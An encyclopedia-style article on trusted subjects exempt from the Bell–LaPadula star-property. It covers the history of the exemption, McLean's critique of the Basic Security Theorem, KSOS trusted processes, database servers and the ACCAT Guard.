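# Trusted subjects: programs exempt from the Bell–LaPadula star-property

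## The star-property and the subjects excused from it

The Bell–LaPadula model is a mathematical description of a computer that holds information at several levels of secrecy and serves users who are not all cleared to see everything. D. Elliott Bell and Leonard LaPadula developed it between 1972 and 1976 at the MITRE Corporation, under contract to the US Air Force, and the builders of many prototype military systems adopted it as their definition of a secure machine. Its best-known rule, the star-property (written with an asterisk in the original reports), forbids a program working at one level to write to anything at a lower level. The model also allows designers to exempt certain programs, called trusted subjects, from this rule. A system needs at least one trusted subject if anyone has to use it to lower a document's classification, and whether the system then keeps its secrets depends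 on what that program does.

### Levels, clearances and the Trojan horse

The model's rules come from the American military scheme for handling paper documents, which Landwehr (1981) describes in *A Survey of Formal Models for Computer Security*. Information has one of four grades (unclassified, confidential, secret, top secret) and may also belong to compartments, such as one for everything about nuclear weapons. Grade and compartments together make up a security level. One level dominates another when its grade is at least as high and its compartments include all of the other's; in symbols, (a, C) ≥ (b, D) exactly when a ≥ b and C ⊇ D. Some pairs of levels are incomparable, such as top secret with no compartment and secret in the nuclear compartment, because neither dominates the other.

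A clearance is a level that the authorities grant a person after an investigation. The person may read information that the clearance dominates if their job requires it. The holder of a document judges this need to know case by case, so controls based on it are called discretionary, while those based only on levels are called mandatory.

With paper documents, security depends largely on the person. An officer with a Secret clearance may read a secret report and then write an unclassified letter, and nobody worries that the pencil will copy the report into the letter. The officer may also sanitize the report by removing the sensitive parts so that the rest can be classified at a lower level, or have it downgraded with its content unchanged if it was classified too high. Landwehr argues that computers change this because the tools are no longer passive. The user of a program that displays documents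 seldom wrote it, and its author may have built it to copy whatever it displays into a file that the author can read. A program that appears useful but secretly leaks information in this way is called a Trojan horse. It runs with the user's clearance, so a rule about reading does not stop it.

The System Development Corporation built ADEPT-50, a time-sharing system, in the late 1960s and installed it at several sites in the Pentagon. ADEPT-50 prevented users from reading upward by opening a file for a job only if the job's level was at least that of the file. It also gave each new file the highest level that the job had accessed so far, but a Trojan horse could still copy classified text into an unclassified file that already existed.

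To close the gap, the Air Force wanted a mechanism and a rule for it to enforce. Roger Schell, then an Air Force major, proposed a mechanism called the security kernel, a small part of the operating system that would contain everything on which security depended and through which every access to data would pass. The working notes that Schell, Downey and Popek wrote between August and November 1972 influenced James Anderson's planning study for the Air Force, which described the same idea in the abstract as a "reference monitor". The notes also influenced the first report by Bell and LaPadula, whose model was to supply the rule.

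### The state and its three properties

Bell and LaPadula treat the computer as a machine that moves from state to state as requests arrive. Subjects are the active parties, in practice programs running for a user. Objects are the files, messages and devices that subjects read or write. McLean, in *A Comment on the "Basic Security Theorem" of Bell and LaPadula*, published in 1985, gives a compact version of the model as it stood in the last of the original reports, the *Unified Exposition* of 1976. A state is a tuple v = (b, M, f, H):

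- b is the set of current accesses. Each member is a triple (s, o, x), meaning that subject s now has object o open in mode x.
- M is the access matrix, with a cell for each subject and object that lists the modes in which that subject may open that object.
- f stands for three functions: clearance(s), the highest level at which s may work; current(s), the level at which s is working now, which clearance(s) must dominate; and class(o), the classification of o.
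- H describes how the objects hang together in a directory tree, and it plays no part in what follows.

A subject needs a current level as well as a clearance because people do not always work at the level of their clearance. *Specification of a Trusted Computing Base (TCB)* (Nibaldi, 1979) gives the example of a user with a Top Secret clearance who drops to Unclassified to update the bowling scores.

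The four access modes differ in whether the subject can observe the object's contents, alter them, or both. Each of the three properties puts its own condition on a triple (s, o, x) in b:

| Mode x | Observe | Alter | Simple security property | Star-property | Discretionary property |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| read | yes | no | clearance(s) ≥ class(o) | current(s) ≥ class(o) | M allows s to read o |
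| append | no | yes | no condition | class(o) ≥ current(s) | M allows s to append to o |
| write | yes | yes | clearance(s) ≥ class(o) | class(o) = current(s) | M allows s to write o |
| execute | no | no | no condition | no condition | M allows s to execute o |

"Write" access in this vocabulary includes reading, so both halves of the star-property apply to it, and together they require the levels to be equal. A state has a property if every triple in b meets that property's condition, and it is secure if it has all three properties.

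The star-property defeats the Trojan horse by letting a program copy information only to the same level or a higher one. Suppose a subject s has object o₂ open for observing and object o₁ open for altering. The star-property requires that class(o₁) ≥ current(s) and current(s) ≥ class(o₂), so class(o₁) ≥ class(o₂). The author of the hostile display program can still write the copying code, but the code can copy the data only into files that the author has no clearance to read.

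### How the exemption entered

Bell and LaPadula (1973) set out the general framework in *Secure Computer Systems*, the first report of the series, dated 1 March. The second report, dated 31 May, introduced the star-property and applied it to every subject. By the end of the year, some subjects were exempt. Bell (1974) re-examined the argument for the rule in the third volume of *Secure Computer Systems*, which he wrote alone and finished in December 1973.

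The argument was that a subject that can write to one object while reading a more highly classified one might put information from the second into the first. The first object's recorded level would then no longer match its contents, and the system would have lost control. To prevent this, the system must not allow that combination of accesses. Bell challenged the word "might". The second report had treated every subject as a possible leaker, but Bell objected that "there may be subjects which will never mix information" of different levels.

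Let S be the set of all subjects, and let S′ be the subset of untrustworthy subjects, those that may mix information. A state satisfies the star-property *relative to S′* if every triple (s, o, x) in b with s in S′ meets the condition in the table. The trusted subjects are the members of S outside S′, and the condition does not apply to them. If S′ = S, the definition is the same as the old rule.

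Bell required that a subject be exempted from the star-property only if somebody has "demonstrated" that it will not cause the kind of compromise the rule exists to prevent. This requirement appears in the prose of the introduction, but in the mathematics S′ is "fixed but arbitrary". It can be any subset of the subjects, and no axiom ties membership in it to evidence. Bell also did not specify what a demonstration would consist of.

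The third volume presents the exemption as a correction to an argument. Fifteen years later, Bell gave a more practical origin in *Concerning "Modeling" of Computer Security*. MITRE had been building a prototype kernel for a secure version of Unix, the original star-property had turned out to be too simple for a working system, and trusted subjects were the result. The dates are consistent with this account. The design document that Bell cites for the prototype, by W. L. Schiller, is dated 30 June 1973, one month after the rule without exceptions and about six months before the rule with them. The two accounts are compatible, though the 1974 volume gives little sign of the engineering problem.

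A trusted subject must still satisfy the other two properties, as the third volume's rules for granting access show. When subject s requests read access to object o, the kernel checks that the matrix entry includes "read", that the clearance of s dominates the classification of o, and that s either is outside S′ or has a current level that dominates the classification of o. Trusted subjects are exempt only from the current-level requirement, so a trusted program with a Secret clearance cannot read a Top Secret file. The simple security property does not restrict append access, so a trusted subject with the right matrix entry may append to an object at any level.

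The 1976 report kept the exemption and extended it to relabelling. Rushby's *The Bell and La Padula Security Model* (1986) restates the report's rules in modern notation. Under the rule for changing an object's classification, an untrusted subject may only raise it. A trusted subject may also lower it, provided that its current level dominates the object's present classification, that every subject with the object open for reading has a current level that dominates the new classification, and that the resulting state still satisfies the star-property for every subject in S′.

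### One program, two files

Take a program p with a Secret clearance, working at current level Secret, with no compartments involved. It has a Secret file F open for reading and an Unclassified file G open for appending, and the access matrix permits both. The set of current accesses is then

b = {(p, F, read), (p, G, append)}.

The simple security property holds, because p's clearance dominates the level of F and the property places no condition on appending to G. The discretionary property holds because both entries are in the matrix. The star-property fails. It allows the read, since Secret dominates Secret, but it would allow the append only if Unclassified dominated Secret. Changing p's current level does not help. At Unclassified the append becomes legal but the read fails, and at Confidential both fail. A level that allowed both would have to dominate Secret and be dominated by Unclassified,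 and no such level exists.

If p is in S′, the state is not secure, and a kernel that follows the rules prevents it by refusing whichever file p tries to open second. If p is outside S′, the star-property does not apply to either triple, and the same state is secure, even though the levels, the matrix and the accesses are unchanged.

Let F be a report on a convoy that contains the route and a paragraph of public weather data. One version of p sanitizes the report correctly by copying the weather into G. Another leaks it by copying the route. Both run through exactly the state above. The reason is explicit in Rushby's restatement, which splits a computer's state into a value state, which holds the contents of the objects, and a protection state, which holds the accesses and levels. Bell and LaPadula's definitions concern only the protection state. Two runs that differ only in what p copies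 have the same protection state, so any property defined on that state holds for both runs or for neither. The kernel therefore stops both versions if p is in S′ and lets both through if it isn't. Somebody has to read the program's code to tell them apart, and can record the finding in the model only by putting p in S′ or leaving it out.

Landwehr thought the model's main practical problems came from the secure operations it disallows. The star-property is stricter than military practice. An officer working on paper may do what p may not, because the officer holds a clearance and the law punishes its abuse. An exemption gives a program the discretion that the paper system gave a person, without the clearance investigation or the legal penalties, so the demonstration Bell asked for has to replace both.

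That demonstration has to cover what other subjects might do while the program runs, as well as what the program itself is meant to do. Rushby reports a case, due to T. Taylor, in which an honest trusted subject leaks information. The subject begins copying one object to another of the same classification, which is harmless. During the copy, a second subject raises the classification of the source and writes more sensitive material into it. The trusted subject keeps copying, so the new material ends up in the object with the lower classification. The star-property would have prevented an untrusted subject from leaking the material this way. One remedy is to forbid changing an object's level while any subject has it open. But the people who check a trusted program have to think of the possibility first, and Rushby considered it quite likely that they would not.

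### The Basic Security Theorem

The 1976 report contains a result with an imposing name, which designers often cited as a reason to prefer this model to its rivals. Call a system secure if every state that it passes through is secure. The Basic Security Theorem is then that a system is secure if and only if its initial state is secure and every transition, from a state with accesses b to one with accesses b\*, meets two conditions for each of the three properties:

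1. Every access in b\* that was not already in b satisfies the property under the new levels and the new matrix.
2. Every access in b that would violate the property under the new levels and matrix is gone from b\*.

Each access in b\* is either new, and so covered by condition 1, or left over from b, and so covered by condition 2. The state after the transition therefore has the property. Since the initial state has it too, every later state has it by induction. Conversely, a transition that breaks either condition leaves a violating access in b\*, so the resulting state is not secure.

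For the star-property, both conditions apply only to accesses by subjects in S′. If S′ is empty, every subject is trusted and there are no accesses to check, so both conditions hold trivially and every possible state satisfies the star-property relative to S′. The theorem remains true as written, but a system now counts as secure under it even if any program can copy Top Secret files into Unclassified ones, provided the program has the clearance to read the former and the matrix entries for both. The remaining protection is roughly that of ADEPT-50, where users cannot read up but a Trojan horse can copy down. Bell's definition allows S′ to be any subset, including the empty one, so the only obstacle is the prose requirement of a demonstration.

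McLean also attacked the theorem by replacing the star-property with a different rule. Marvin Schaefer had formulated a "†-property" and challenged McLean to prove the theorem for it. A state has the †-property if, for every triple (s, o, write) in b, the current level of s dominates the classification of o. This roughly reverses the star-property, so a subject working at Secret can write into an unclassified file or, in McLean's example, into the *Washington Post*. If a secure state is defined as one with the simple security property, the †-property and the discretionary property, the "Basic Security Theorem" for the new model follows.

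McLean's proof is the induction already given. If all states before the nth have the †-property, the nth can lack it only if the last transition granted a new write access that violates the property, or kept an old one that violates it under the new levels. Condition 1 rules out the first case and condition 2 the second. Conversely, if a transition breaks either condition, b\* contains a triple that violates the †-property, so the new state lacks it. McLean adds that the simple security property could be replaced in the same way, with a rule that lets users read only what lies above their clearance.

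McLean concludes that the Basic Security Theorem is a fact about systems whose states can be numbered in order and has no particular connection with security. Rushby generalizes the point, observing that any effectively decidable property of a state has its own Basic Security Theorem. McLean sees two serious questions about a security model, whether its definition captures what people mean by security and whether a given real system meets that definition. The theorem helps with neither, and McLean thought that researchers who proved a version of it for each new model were wasting their time. The paper acknowledges that Bell and LaPadula seem to have wanted only to show that security is preserved from one state to the next, so that a designer can check transitions one at a time. It also points out that the theorem as printed in 1976 was false, because their definition of a secure system placed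 no condition on the initial state.

McLean (1987) also argued against the Bell–LaPadula definition of security, using an imaginary computer named System Z. Its only transition lowers every object to the lowest level and gives every subject every kind of access to every object. Each resulting state still meets the definition, and McLean concluded that the definition was inadequate.

In a 1988 reply, Bell stops using the theorem as an argument for the model. Bell writes that being inductive is "not a justification, just a pleasant characteristic" of a property, and that undesirable properties can be inductive too. Bell calls the slip about the initial state "real but not devastating", but does not give way on System Z. Bell argues that the model defines "security" as three chosen facets of the ordinary notion and leaves out the rest, much as Newton's mechanics leaves out nuclear forces. Anyone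 who dislikes the transition in System Z can exclude it by adding the principle of tranquility from the first report, under which the levels of objects never change after the initial state. Bell took the same position in a later talk. According to a summary by CERIAS, the information-security centre at Purdue University, Bell argued that "security" has no meaning until somebody defines it, and that settling the definition means negotiating over policy.

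Bell also gives an example in which the customer requires System Z's transition. Artillery observers carry a backpack computer that must destroy its secrets if they are about to be captured. It overwrites every file and then regrades them all to Unclassified. In the model, the overwriting appears only as a series of writes, while the regrading looks like System Z's transition.

The example succeeds as a defence of flexibility, but it also puts Bell closer to McLean than the tone of the exchange suggests. The soldier's computer avoids a catastrophic leak only because the files were blank when their labels changed, and the model's state does not record what files contain. Bell's account of how to use a model covers such facts under faithful representation, the work of describing the real system correctly in the model's terms before analysing it. A mistake at this stage makes the analysis worthless.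 Choosing S′ is part of this work, and every later theorem about the system remains true even if the designer leaves a leaking program out of S′.

### Trusted and trustworthy

Someone must therefore establish that the right programs are in S′ and that the kernel enforces the rules on them. Nibaldi's specification, also written at MITRE, requires that a reference monitor be complete (check every access), protect itself from interference, and be simple enough for people to verify. Hardware makes it practical to check every access. Each process can access only a virtual memory made of segments, and each segment has a descriptor that holds its physical address, its length and the permitted modes of access. The kernel checks the policy once, when it sets up the descriptor. After that, the hardware compares every reference with the descriptor and aborts any that the descriptor does not permit.

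Users have to log in, change the level of a file, print, and restore the disk from a backup, and several of these jobs involve breaking the star-property or handling the labels it depends on. Designers could put the programs for these jobs inside the kernel, but they usually keep them outside as trusted processes, the operating-system term for trusted subjects, because two smaller pieces of software are easier to verify than one large one. The kernel and the trusted processes together form the trusted computing base (TCB), all of which must work correctly. Different projects also called trusted processes "privileged", "responsible" or "non-kernel security-related" software, which suggests some unease about what they were.

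The boundary of the TCB matters because, if a proof shows that the TCB enforces the policy, nobody has to examine the software outside it. A text editor may contain any number of Trojan horses and still be unable to write down. Nibaldi describes such a proof as a chain in which a formal specification of the TCB upholds the model, the program implements the specification, and the machine code implements the program. The first link fails for a trusted subject, because the program is meant to do something the general model forbids. Nibaldi proposes a second model for that subject alone, which sets out the ways it may violate the first, and a second chain of proof that starts from the second model. The second model and its proof become more complex as the program's duties widen.

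This gives some substance to the demonstration that Bell had required in 1974, and it also shows why *trusted* and *trustworthy* need to be distinguished. A component is *trusted* if its failure can break the policy, and *trustworthy* if there is good evidence that it will not fail. Being trusted depends on the component's place in the design, so a designer can make a program trusted by leaving it out of S′. Establishing that the program is trustworthy takes work, and the attempt may fail. Bell's third volume uses both words for the exempt subjects, which is harmless so long as every exemption follows a demonstration. In a system that grants exemptions without one, an unexamined program is as much a trusted subject as one with a complete proof, and the formal model contains no distinction between them.

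In 1981 Landwehr listed six designs and implementations based on the Bell–LaPadula model or a modification of it. He observed that sanitizing, downgrading and every other change of level had to go through trusted processes, and that the model gave "little guidance" on which processes to trust. Designers could obey the model and omit functions that their users needed, or they could provide those functions, even one as ordinary as a printer spooler, by relying heavily on the exemption for trusted processes.

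## Spoolers, backup tools and database servers that write down

A printer spooler collects files from many users, keeps them in a queue and prints them one at a time. It doesn't need to reveal one user's files to another, yet spoolers commonly ended up with permission to write down. Rushby's *Design and Verification of Secure Systems* (1981) explains how this happened.

### A printer queue under the star-property

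A user working at Unclassified might print a memo on a machine that holds files up to Top Secret. The spooler has to read spool files (the queued copies) of every level, so it runs at Top Secret. The designer still has to choose a level for the spool files.

If the spooler and its queue are Top Secret, every step obeys the rules. The user's process appends a copy of the memo up to the queue, and the spooler reads, prints and deletes the copy at its own level. But the user cannot read anything at Top Secret, so cannot check the queue to see whether the memo has printed.

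Designers therefore usually keep each spool file at its owner's level. The user can then inspect the memo's spool file, and the spooler can read and print it. But the spooler must also delete the file afterward. Deletion counts as a write, and the star-property forbids a Top Secret spooler from writing to an Unclassified file. The kernel blocks the deletion, and used spool files pile up on the disk.

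The kernel blocks the spooler from deleting an unclassified file after printing it because any unclassified program can see whether the file still exists. A hostile spooler could leak a Top Secret document one bit at a time by deleting a file for a 1 and leaving it for a 0. An honest spooler's deletion reveals only that the job is done. Using an Unclassified cleanup program instead doesn't help much, because the spooler would have to tell it when printing had finished, and that message would itself be a write-down. The cleanup program could delete every file after a day, but files delayed by a paper jam could then be lost before they were printed. Rushby concludes that an acceptable service seems to require making the spooler a trusted process.

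A spooler needs the exemption only to delete files it has printed, but the exemption also lets it copy any Top Secret file into any Unclassified file for which it has the matrix entries. The star-property also doesn't cover what people want from a spooler. Rushby's examples are that it should print the right classification on each job's header page, keep parts of one job out of another, and never feed one user's input back to a different user. A spooler that obeyed the star-property could still stamp "Unclassified" on a Top Secret printout. Exempting the spooler removes the star-property without replacing it with a suitable restriction.

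### The trusted processes of KSOS

Many programs in the Kernelized Secure Operating System (KSOS) ended up in the same position as the spooler. Ford Aerospace began designing KSOS in 1977, under a Defense Department contract, as a provably secure replacement for UNIX on the PDP-11/70 minicomputer. Ford Aerospace's *Secure Minicomputer Operating System (KSOS) Final Report* (1981) describes the system's three parts: a security kernel, an emulator that gave programs the usual UNIX interface, and separate support programs. Some of the support programs, called trusted processes, were allowed to break one or more of the kernel's rules.

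Ford Aerospace's *Secure Minicomputer Operating System (KSOS) System Specification (Type A)* (1980) lists the services that the support programs had to provide. The table shows the main ones that needed special powers, together with device assignment, which comes from the final report:

| Program | Job | Why it needs special powers |
|---|---|---|
| Line printer daemon | Prints queued files with the correct headers and footers, then deletes them | It deletes files below its own level |
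| Dump and restore | Copies whole file systems to tape and back | Restoring writes low files from a tape that also holds high ones |
| Network daemon | Divides one stream of network data among many processes | On a multilevel network it handles several levels at once |
| File level changer | Regrades files and logs every attempt | It can lower a label |
| User level changer | Moves a user to another working level | It changes a label that the other rules rely on |
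| Device assignment | Gives an idle tape drive the level and owner of the user who asks for it | It relabels a shared device |

Backup tools need the exemption only to restore files. Making a backup breaks no rule, because a program at the highest level may read every file on the disk and write a tape at that level. To restore the files, the program reads that tape and has to recreate the unclassified files as unclassified, which the star-property forbids. If the program obeyed the property, every file it restored after a disk failure would become Top Secret.

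In ordinary UNIX these jobs belong to the "superuser", an account that may read or write any file. Any program a superuser runs gets the same access, which makes the account an ideal target for a Trojan horse. KSOS replaced the superuser with specific privileges attached to individual program files, and it restricted who could run each program. Any user could change working level, only the operator could dump a file system to tape, and only the administrator could alter a clearance.

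The KSOS designers also tried to avoid privileges where they could. Spooling and mail both have to transfer data from the user's ownership to the service's. In KSOS the user's own process read the file and passed the data over a channel to a second process, which stored it in a file that the service owned, so the service didn't need a privilege to read the user's file. With this arrangement the mail system needed no exemption, but the spooler still needed one to delete files.

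The file level changer opened a file for exclusive use, displayed it to the user, changed its level and closed it. Nobody could alter the file between the display and the change, so users always regraded the text they had just read. This prevents the kind of leak that the honest program in Taylor's example allowed. However, the lock also kept out other trusted programs that might have scanned the file to help with the decision.

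The operator's tool for repairing file systems had too much privilege. It could change a file's security level and reassign disk blocks from one file to another, which gave the operator a power meant for the administrator.

A program may need checking even if it is exempt from none of the kernel's rules. For example, Ford Aerospace classed the special editor that the administrator used to change the file of users' clearances as untrusted. The editor broke none of the kernel's rules, so it needed no privileges. But a Trojan horse in it could have raised a spy's clearance to Top Secret, and the kernel, applying its rules correctly, would then have let the spy read everything. The editor was trusted in the sense used here, because its failure could break the policy.

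### What an exempt function still had to obey

Ford Aerospace's subcontractor, SRI International, reformulated the Bell–LaPadula model so that a computer could check specifications against it. Landwehr gives the version for KSOS. It describes the system through function references and state variables. A function reference f is a call with particular arguments, and its level is normally the current level of the process that makes it. A state variable v is any item that the system remembers from one call to the next. Writing L for the security level, the model has three conditions:

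- (a) If f depends on v, then L(v) ≤ L(f).
- (b) If f may change v₂ in a way that depends on v₁, then L(v₁) ≤ L(v₂).
- (c) If f may affect v, then L(f) ≤ L(v).

Condition (a) corresponds roughly to the simple security property and (c) to the star-property. Condition (b) covers functions that both read and write. Each condition also has a version with the inequalities reversed for integrity, which grades how far people can rely on the data.

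Condition (b) makes exemptions awkward. A function that keeps to it can never move information down. Dropping it altogether would go too far the other way, since f could then copy a variable that it had no clearance to read. SRI therefore split it in two:

- (b′) L(v₁) ≤ L(v₂) or L(v₁) ≤ L(f).
- (b″) L(v₁) ≤ L(v₂) or L(f) ≤ L(v₂).

The two halves together are equivalent to (b). If (b) holds, the first alternative is true in both. Conversely, suppose both halves hold but L(v₁) ≤ L(v₂) does not. Then the second alternative must be true in both, so L(v₁) ≤ L(f) ≤ L(v₂), which is a contradiction.

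In the split version, (a) and (b′) make up the simple security property, and (b″) and (c) make up the star-property. A function allowed to violate the star-property must still satisfy (a) and (b′). A function allowed to violate the simple integrity rule, which forbids reading data of lower integrity, must satisfy the integrity versions of (b″) and (c).

The first alternative in (b′) covers calls from a low level that have side effects at a higher one. When an Unclassified process adds a message to a Secret queue, the queue's new contents depend on its old contents, which are above the caller's level. So the second alternative fails, but the first holds because that information has only moved from Secret to Secret.

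Now apply the conditions to the spooler's deletion. Let f be the call that deletes the memo's spool file, made at Top Secret. Let v₁ be the spooler's Top Secret record of what it has printed, and v₂ the existence of the Unclassified spool file:

| Condition | What it requires here | Result |
|---|---|---|
| (a) | Top Secret ≤ Top Secret | holds |
| (b′) | Top Secret ≤ Unclassified, or Top Secret ≤ Top Secret | holds |
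| (b″) | Top Secret ≤ Unclassified, or Top Secret ≤ Unclassified | fails |
| (c) | Top Secret ≤ Unclassified | fails |

The exemption lifts only the two conditions that fail. The other two still restrict the spooler, so a version running at Secret could not pass on anything from a Top Secret variable. But the table would be the same if v₁ were a war plan and v₂ were the text of an unclassified newsletter. The conditions compare only levels, so they cannot distinguish a harmless deletion from wholesale copying.

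Feiertag, one of the model's developers, told Landwehr that the published version of the split had two erroneous equals signs in (b′) and omitted (b″).

### What Ford Aerospace managed to prove

Feiertag (1980) described the checking method in *A Technique for Proving Specifications Are Multilevel Secure*. A program reads a formal specification and generates formulas that, if true, imply that the specification satisfies the model. A theorem prover then tries to prove them. Ford Aerospace and SRI ran this on the specifications of all 34 kernel calls and found many errors that several rounds of human inspection had missed. In a February 1980 run, the tool generated 1,596 formulas, of which 138 remained unproved. An unproved formula could indicate a real flaw, a true statement that the prover could not prove, or a deliberate violation that the trusted software needed.

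Even the kernel proofs had limits. In several runs the input included a false assumption about which levels could interact, so the prover proved formulas that it should not have. Funding also ran out before anyone could run the tools on the final version of the specification.

The trusted processes had nothing comparable. The 1980 specification had called for formal specifications of all trusted software and for proofs that the design satisfied the government's model, but Ford Aerospace verified none of the specifications for the support programs. This was partly because of organisational trouble, but there was also no model to verify them against, since the existing one could not directly represent privileges. According to the final report, it was "quite difficult to define exactly what 'correct' means for a trusted process", and each case needed separate treatment. In the meantime, Ford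 Aerospace inserted artificial delays to limit how fast users could make a trusted service violate the model.

Support programs made up over half of the software written for KSOS. Some of them, such as the mail system, had no privileges, so the exempt code was a smaller share, but it was still large, partly because the designers had kept the kernel small. They moved work that an operating system normally does in its kernel, such as managing directories and mounting disks, into support programs, which were orders of magnitude larger and more complex than the equivalent kernel functions would have been. The usual argument for keeping trusted processes outside the kernel assumes that dividing the software adds little to its total size, but in KSOS it added a lot.

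The KSOS developers blamed a "mismatch" between the idealized policy and what users needed in practice. Rushby, who quotes them, thought the deeper fault was the idea that a kernel should impose one policy on every component. On this view, a spooler's requirements depend as much on its function as on the policy of the whole system. Nobody knew how to combine the properties proved of a kernel with those proved of the trusted processes, and Rushby saw no real justification for calling such systems verified. The same problem was especially clear in the guard built on KSOS, because all its downward traffic went through trusted processes.

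### Naming exemptions and justifying them

*A Guide to Understanding Security Modeling in Trusted Systems* (Williams 1992) gave designers in this position official US government advice. Williams wrote it for the National Computer Security Center, which evaluated commercial systems for the Defense Department, and insists that exemptions are "not a license to violate policy". The rules a system actually enforces depend on what its exempt programs do as well as what its ordinary programs may do. A model that leaves out the exempt programs therefore misdescribes the system, and the error tends to matter more when those programs interact heavily with the rest of it.

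The advice begins with identifying the exemptions, sorting them by the kind of requirement they relax (mandatory access, discretionary access, auditing or assurance of service), and tying each named exemption to one kind of function. A process without a given exemption cannot interfere with the corresponding requirement. In the Army Secure Operating System (ASOS), for example, every process obeys the star-property unless it has the "security-star-exemption". A process can receive this exemption only if the system's builders assigned it to the program in advance and the parent process passes it on. Most processes can never have it, and the rest run with it only when they need it. SELinux, the access-control system later built into Linux, also grants its exemptions by name.

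How a program gets its privileges matters as much as what they are. UNIX has long had "set-user-id" programs, which run with their owner's permissions no matter who starts them. A badly designed one lets its caller copy the owner's private files. Williams notes that the designers of Secure Xenix, a hardened UNIX of the 1980s, considered changes to this mechanism. KSOS had to extend the idea from owners to security levels. Some programs had to start at the user's level, some at a fixed level, and others at a level relative to the user or to one of the program's parameters. A trusted program looked up each program's level in a table and started it there, so few programs needed the privilege to change level themselves.

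Running with an exemption only when necessary also addresses a problem in KSOS. Its programs had only the privileges they needed, but they kept them for the whole run, so a verifier had to examine the whole program. Ford Aerospace concluded that it would have been better to let programs switch privileges on just before a critical section and off just after it. This would make honest mistakes easier to find, but it wouldn't confine hostile code elsewhere in the same program, which could also switch the privileges on.

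Another way to limit an exemption is to give it a range. In GEMSOS, another secure operating system, each subject has two labels in place of a single current level. View-max is the highest level from which it may read, and alter-min is the lowest level to which it may write:

- s may read o only if view-max(s) ≥ class(o);
- s may write to o only if class(o) ≥ alter-min(s).

When view-max and alter-min are equal, these rules are the two halves of the ordinary star-property. When view-max is higher, the program is exempt within the range between them. A program with view-max at Secret and alter-min at Confidential can leak Secret data to Confidential files, but it cannot write to an Unclassified file or read a Top Secret one. A spooler that serves every level needs the full range, so the labels don't restrict it. They would restrict a spooler for a printer that handles nothing above Secret,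 and in KSOS the operator had to set a maximum level for the printer before it could start.

The designer needs to justify the use of each exemption, and Williams recommends explicit constraints on what the exempt program may do. Choosing how much to specify is difficult. The security requirement is usually much weaker than a full description of correct behaviour. A terminal server, for instance, has to give each user a trusted path to the TCB and prevent leaks between that path and other channels, and a model need not cover much else. Rushby's three requirements for a spooler are similarly limited, leaving out fonts and the order of the queue.

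Programs for administrators and operators are harder, because their safety depends partly on the person. Williams recommends dividing the constraints between automatic checks in the software and written procedures in the manual, so that a reader can see, for example, what stops an administrator from editing the audit trail to falsify evidence about other users. Such constraints often apply to a sequence of events. For example, KSOS requires a user to see a file before regrading it, and a definition that covers only one state at a time cannot express that rule. Designers often left these programs out of their models because few people used them and they lacked accepted examples. Williams calls this argument weak, because people in such roles can do more damage.

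This advice goes further than the "little guidance" that Landwehr found in the model in 1981, but the evaluation criteria did not explicitly require models of exempt subjects. For subjects exempt from the mandatory rules, Williams often considers it enough to search for covert channels, the unintended paths by which information can escape. A trusted database server, however, needs its own model even if it conforms to the general policy.

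### The database server as one trusted subject

A database server answers all its users' queries from one shared store. If the users have different clearances, some part of the system must keep data at different levels separate. The early designs, two of which Landwehr describes, left this to the operating system.

Hinke and Schaefer designed their database system in 1975 for Multics, the time-sharing system to which Bell and LaPadula applied their model in their 1976 report. They gave each column of a table its own level and stored it in its own segment, the unit of storage that the Multics kernel protects. Suppose a table has an Unclassified column of suppliers and a Secret column of the parts they make. When a user working at Unclassified runs the database program, it runs at that level too, so the kernel lets it open the supplier segment but not the parts segment. The program needs no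 exemption from the star-property, so security depends only on the kernel.

Updates are less convenient, because a subject has to work at exactly an entry's level to read and change it. A user at Secret can see the whole row but can change only the part entry, while a user at Unclassified can change only the supplier entry. To correct both in one session, a user has to change level partway through. Grohn argued in 1976 that for convenience all the columns would have to be at the same level, and so gave each table a single level. That makes the labels coarser still. If one supplier's contract is secret and the other forty are not, the designer has to classify the whole table as Secret or split it in two.

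The alternative is to run the server as a single trusted subject. It keeps the whole database in files at the highest level, attaches its own labels to columns, rows or single entries, and filters each answer to suit the user who asked. Let d be the server, T a Top Secret file that holds the table, and R the channel for replies to an Unclassified user. While d answers a query, the set of current accesses includes

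{(d, T, read), (d, R, append)}.

This is the same pattern as the program that either sanitized a convoy report or leaked it. The kernel checks whether d can read T and write to R, but not which rows go into the reply. All the server code that handles unfiltered data (the code that interprets queries, searches indexes and assembles results) can therefore leak Top Secret information, and belongs to the TCB. The server uses its exemption for every answer it gives to a user below the highest level, whereas a spooler uses its exemption once per job, to delete a file.

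Narrowing the range of levels, as in GEMSOS, doesn't help a server that has to read at the highest level and reply at the lowest. The server also interacts with ordinary subjects about as much as a program can, and according to Williams, that is when an unmodelled exemption does the most harm. It needs a separate model because it extends what the TCB offers its users. A proof about the kernel covers access to files, but database users work with rows and queries. The National Computer Security Center had already published a separate interpretation of its operating system criteria for databases, the *Trusted Database Management System Interpretation*, in 1991.

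A trusted server is sometimes a reasonable choice. Rushby describes a file server on its own machine, which runs a single program and no user code. Only that program needs verifying, and SRI's flow conditions suit it well because it only stores labelled files and gives them to users whose levels are known. A database server does much more processing on data before returning it, so its model and proof have to cover more.

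A trusted server can also protect facts that are secret only in combination, which a kernel cannot do. In Landwehr's example, a picture of the Statue of Liberty and the caption "Location of secret Particle Beam Weapon" could each be unclassified, while the pair might be Top Secret. If a database stores pictures and captions in two Unclassified segments, the kernel will let any user open both. A trusted server can detect a query that joins them and refuse it. To stop a user from requesting the picture today and the caption tomorrow, it would also have to keep a record of what it has released to each user, which adds still more code that somebody has to verify.

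## Guards that pass messages from high to low networks

A guard sits between a more secret network and a less secret one. Its main job, unlike a database server's, is to decide which messages may pass down. The American armed forces wanted guards in the late 1970s because they kept databases of different secrecy levels on separate computers, and staff with access only to the lower one sometimes needed facts from the higher. A guard let the two systems exchange messages while both kept running ordinary commercial software. Neither system had to enforce levels itself, so the guard was the main new component whose failure could leak secrets to the less secret system.

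### One query through the ACCAT Guard

The original guard was named after ACCAT, the Advanced Command and Control Architectural Testbed. Logicon, a defence contractor, built the guard for the Navy and ARPA, the Defense Department's research agency, and planned to run it on KSOS. *The advent of trusted computer operating systems*, a 1980 conference paper by Walker, describes how it would work. Suppose an officer on a Secret system wants to know which ports a ship has visited, and the answer is in a Top Secret database.

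1. The query goes up through the Guard to the Top Secret database.
2. The database returns a reply, which may contain Top Secret material, such as the name of the agent who saw the ship.
3. An operator, or an application program on the Guard, sanitizes the reply by removing the name.
4. The security kernel displays the sanitized reply to a Security Watch Officer, who decides what classification it now deserves.
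5. If the answer is Secret or lower, the Guard forwards the reply. Otherwise the reply goes back to step 3.

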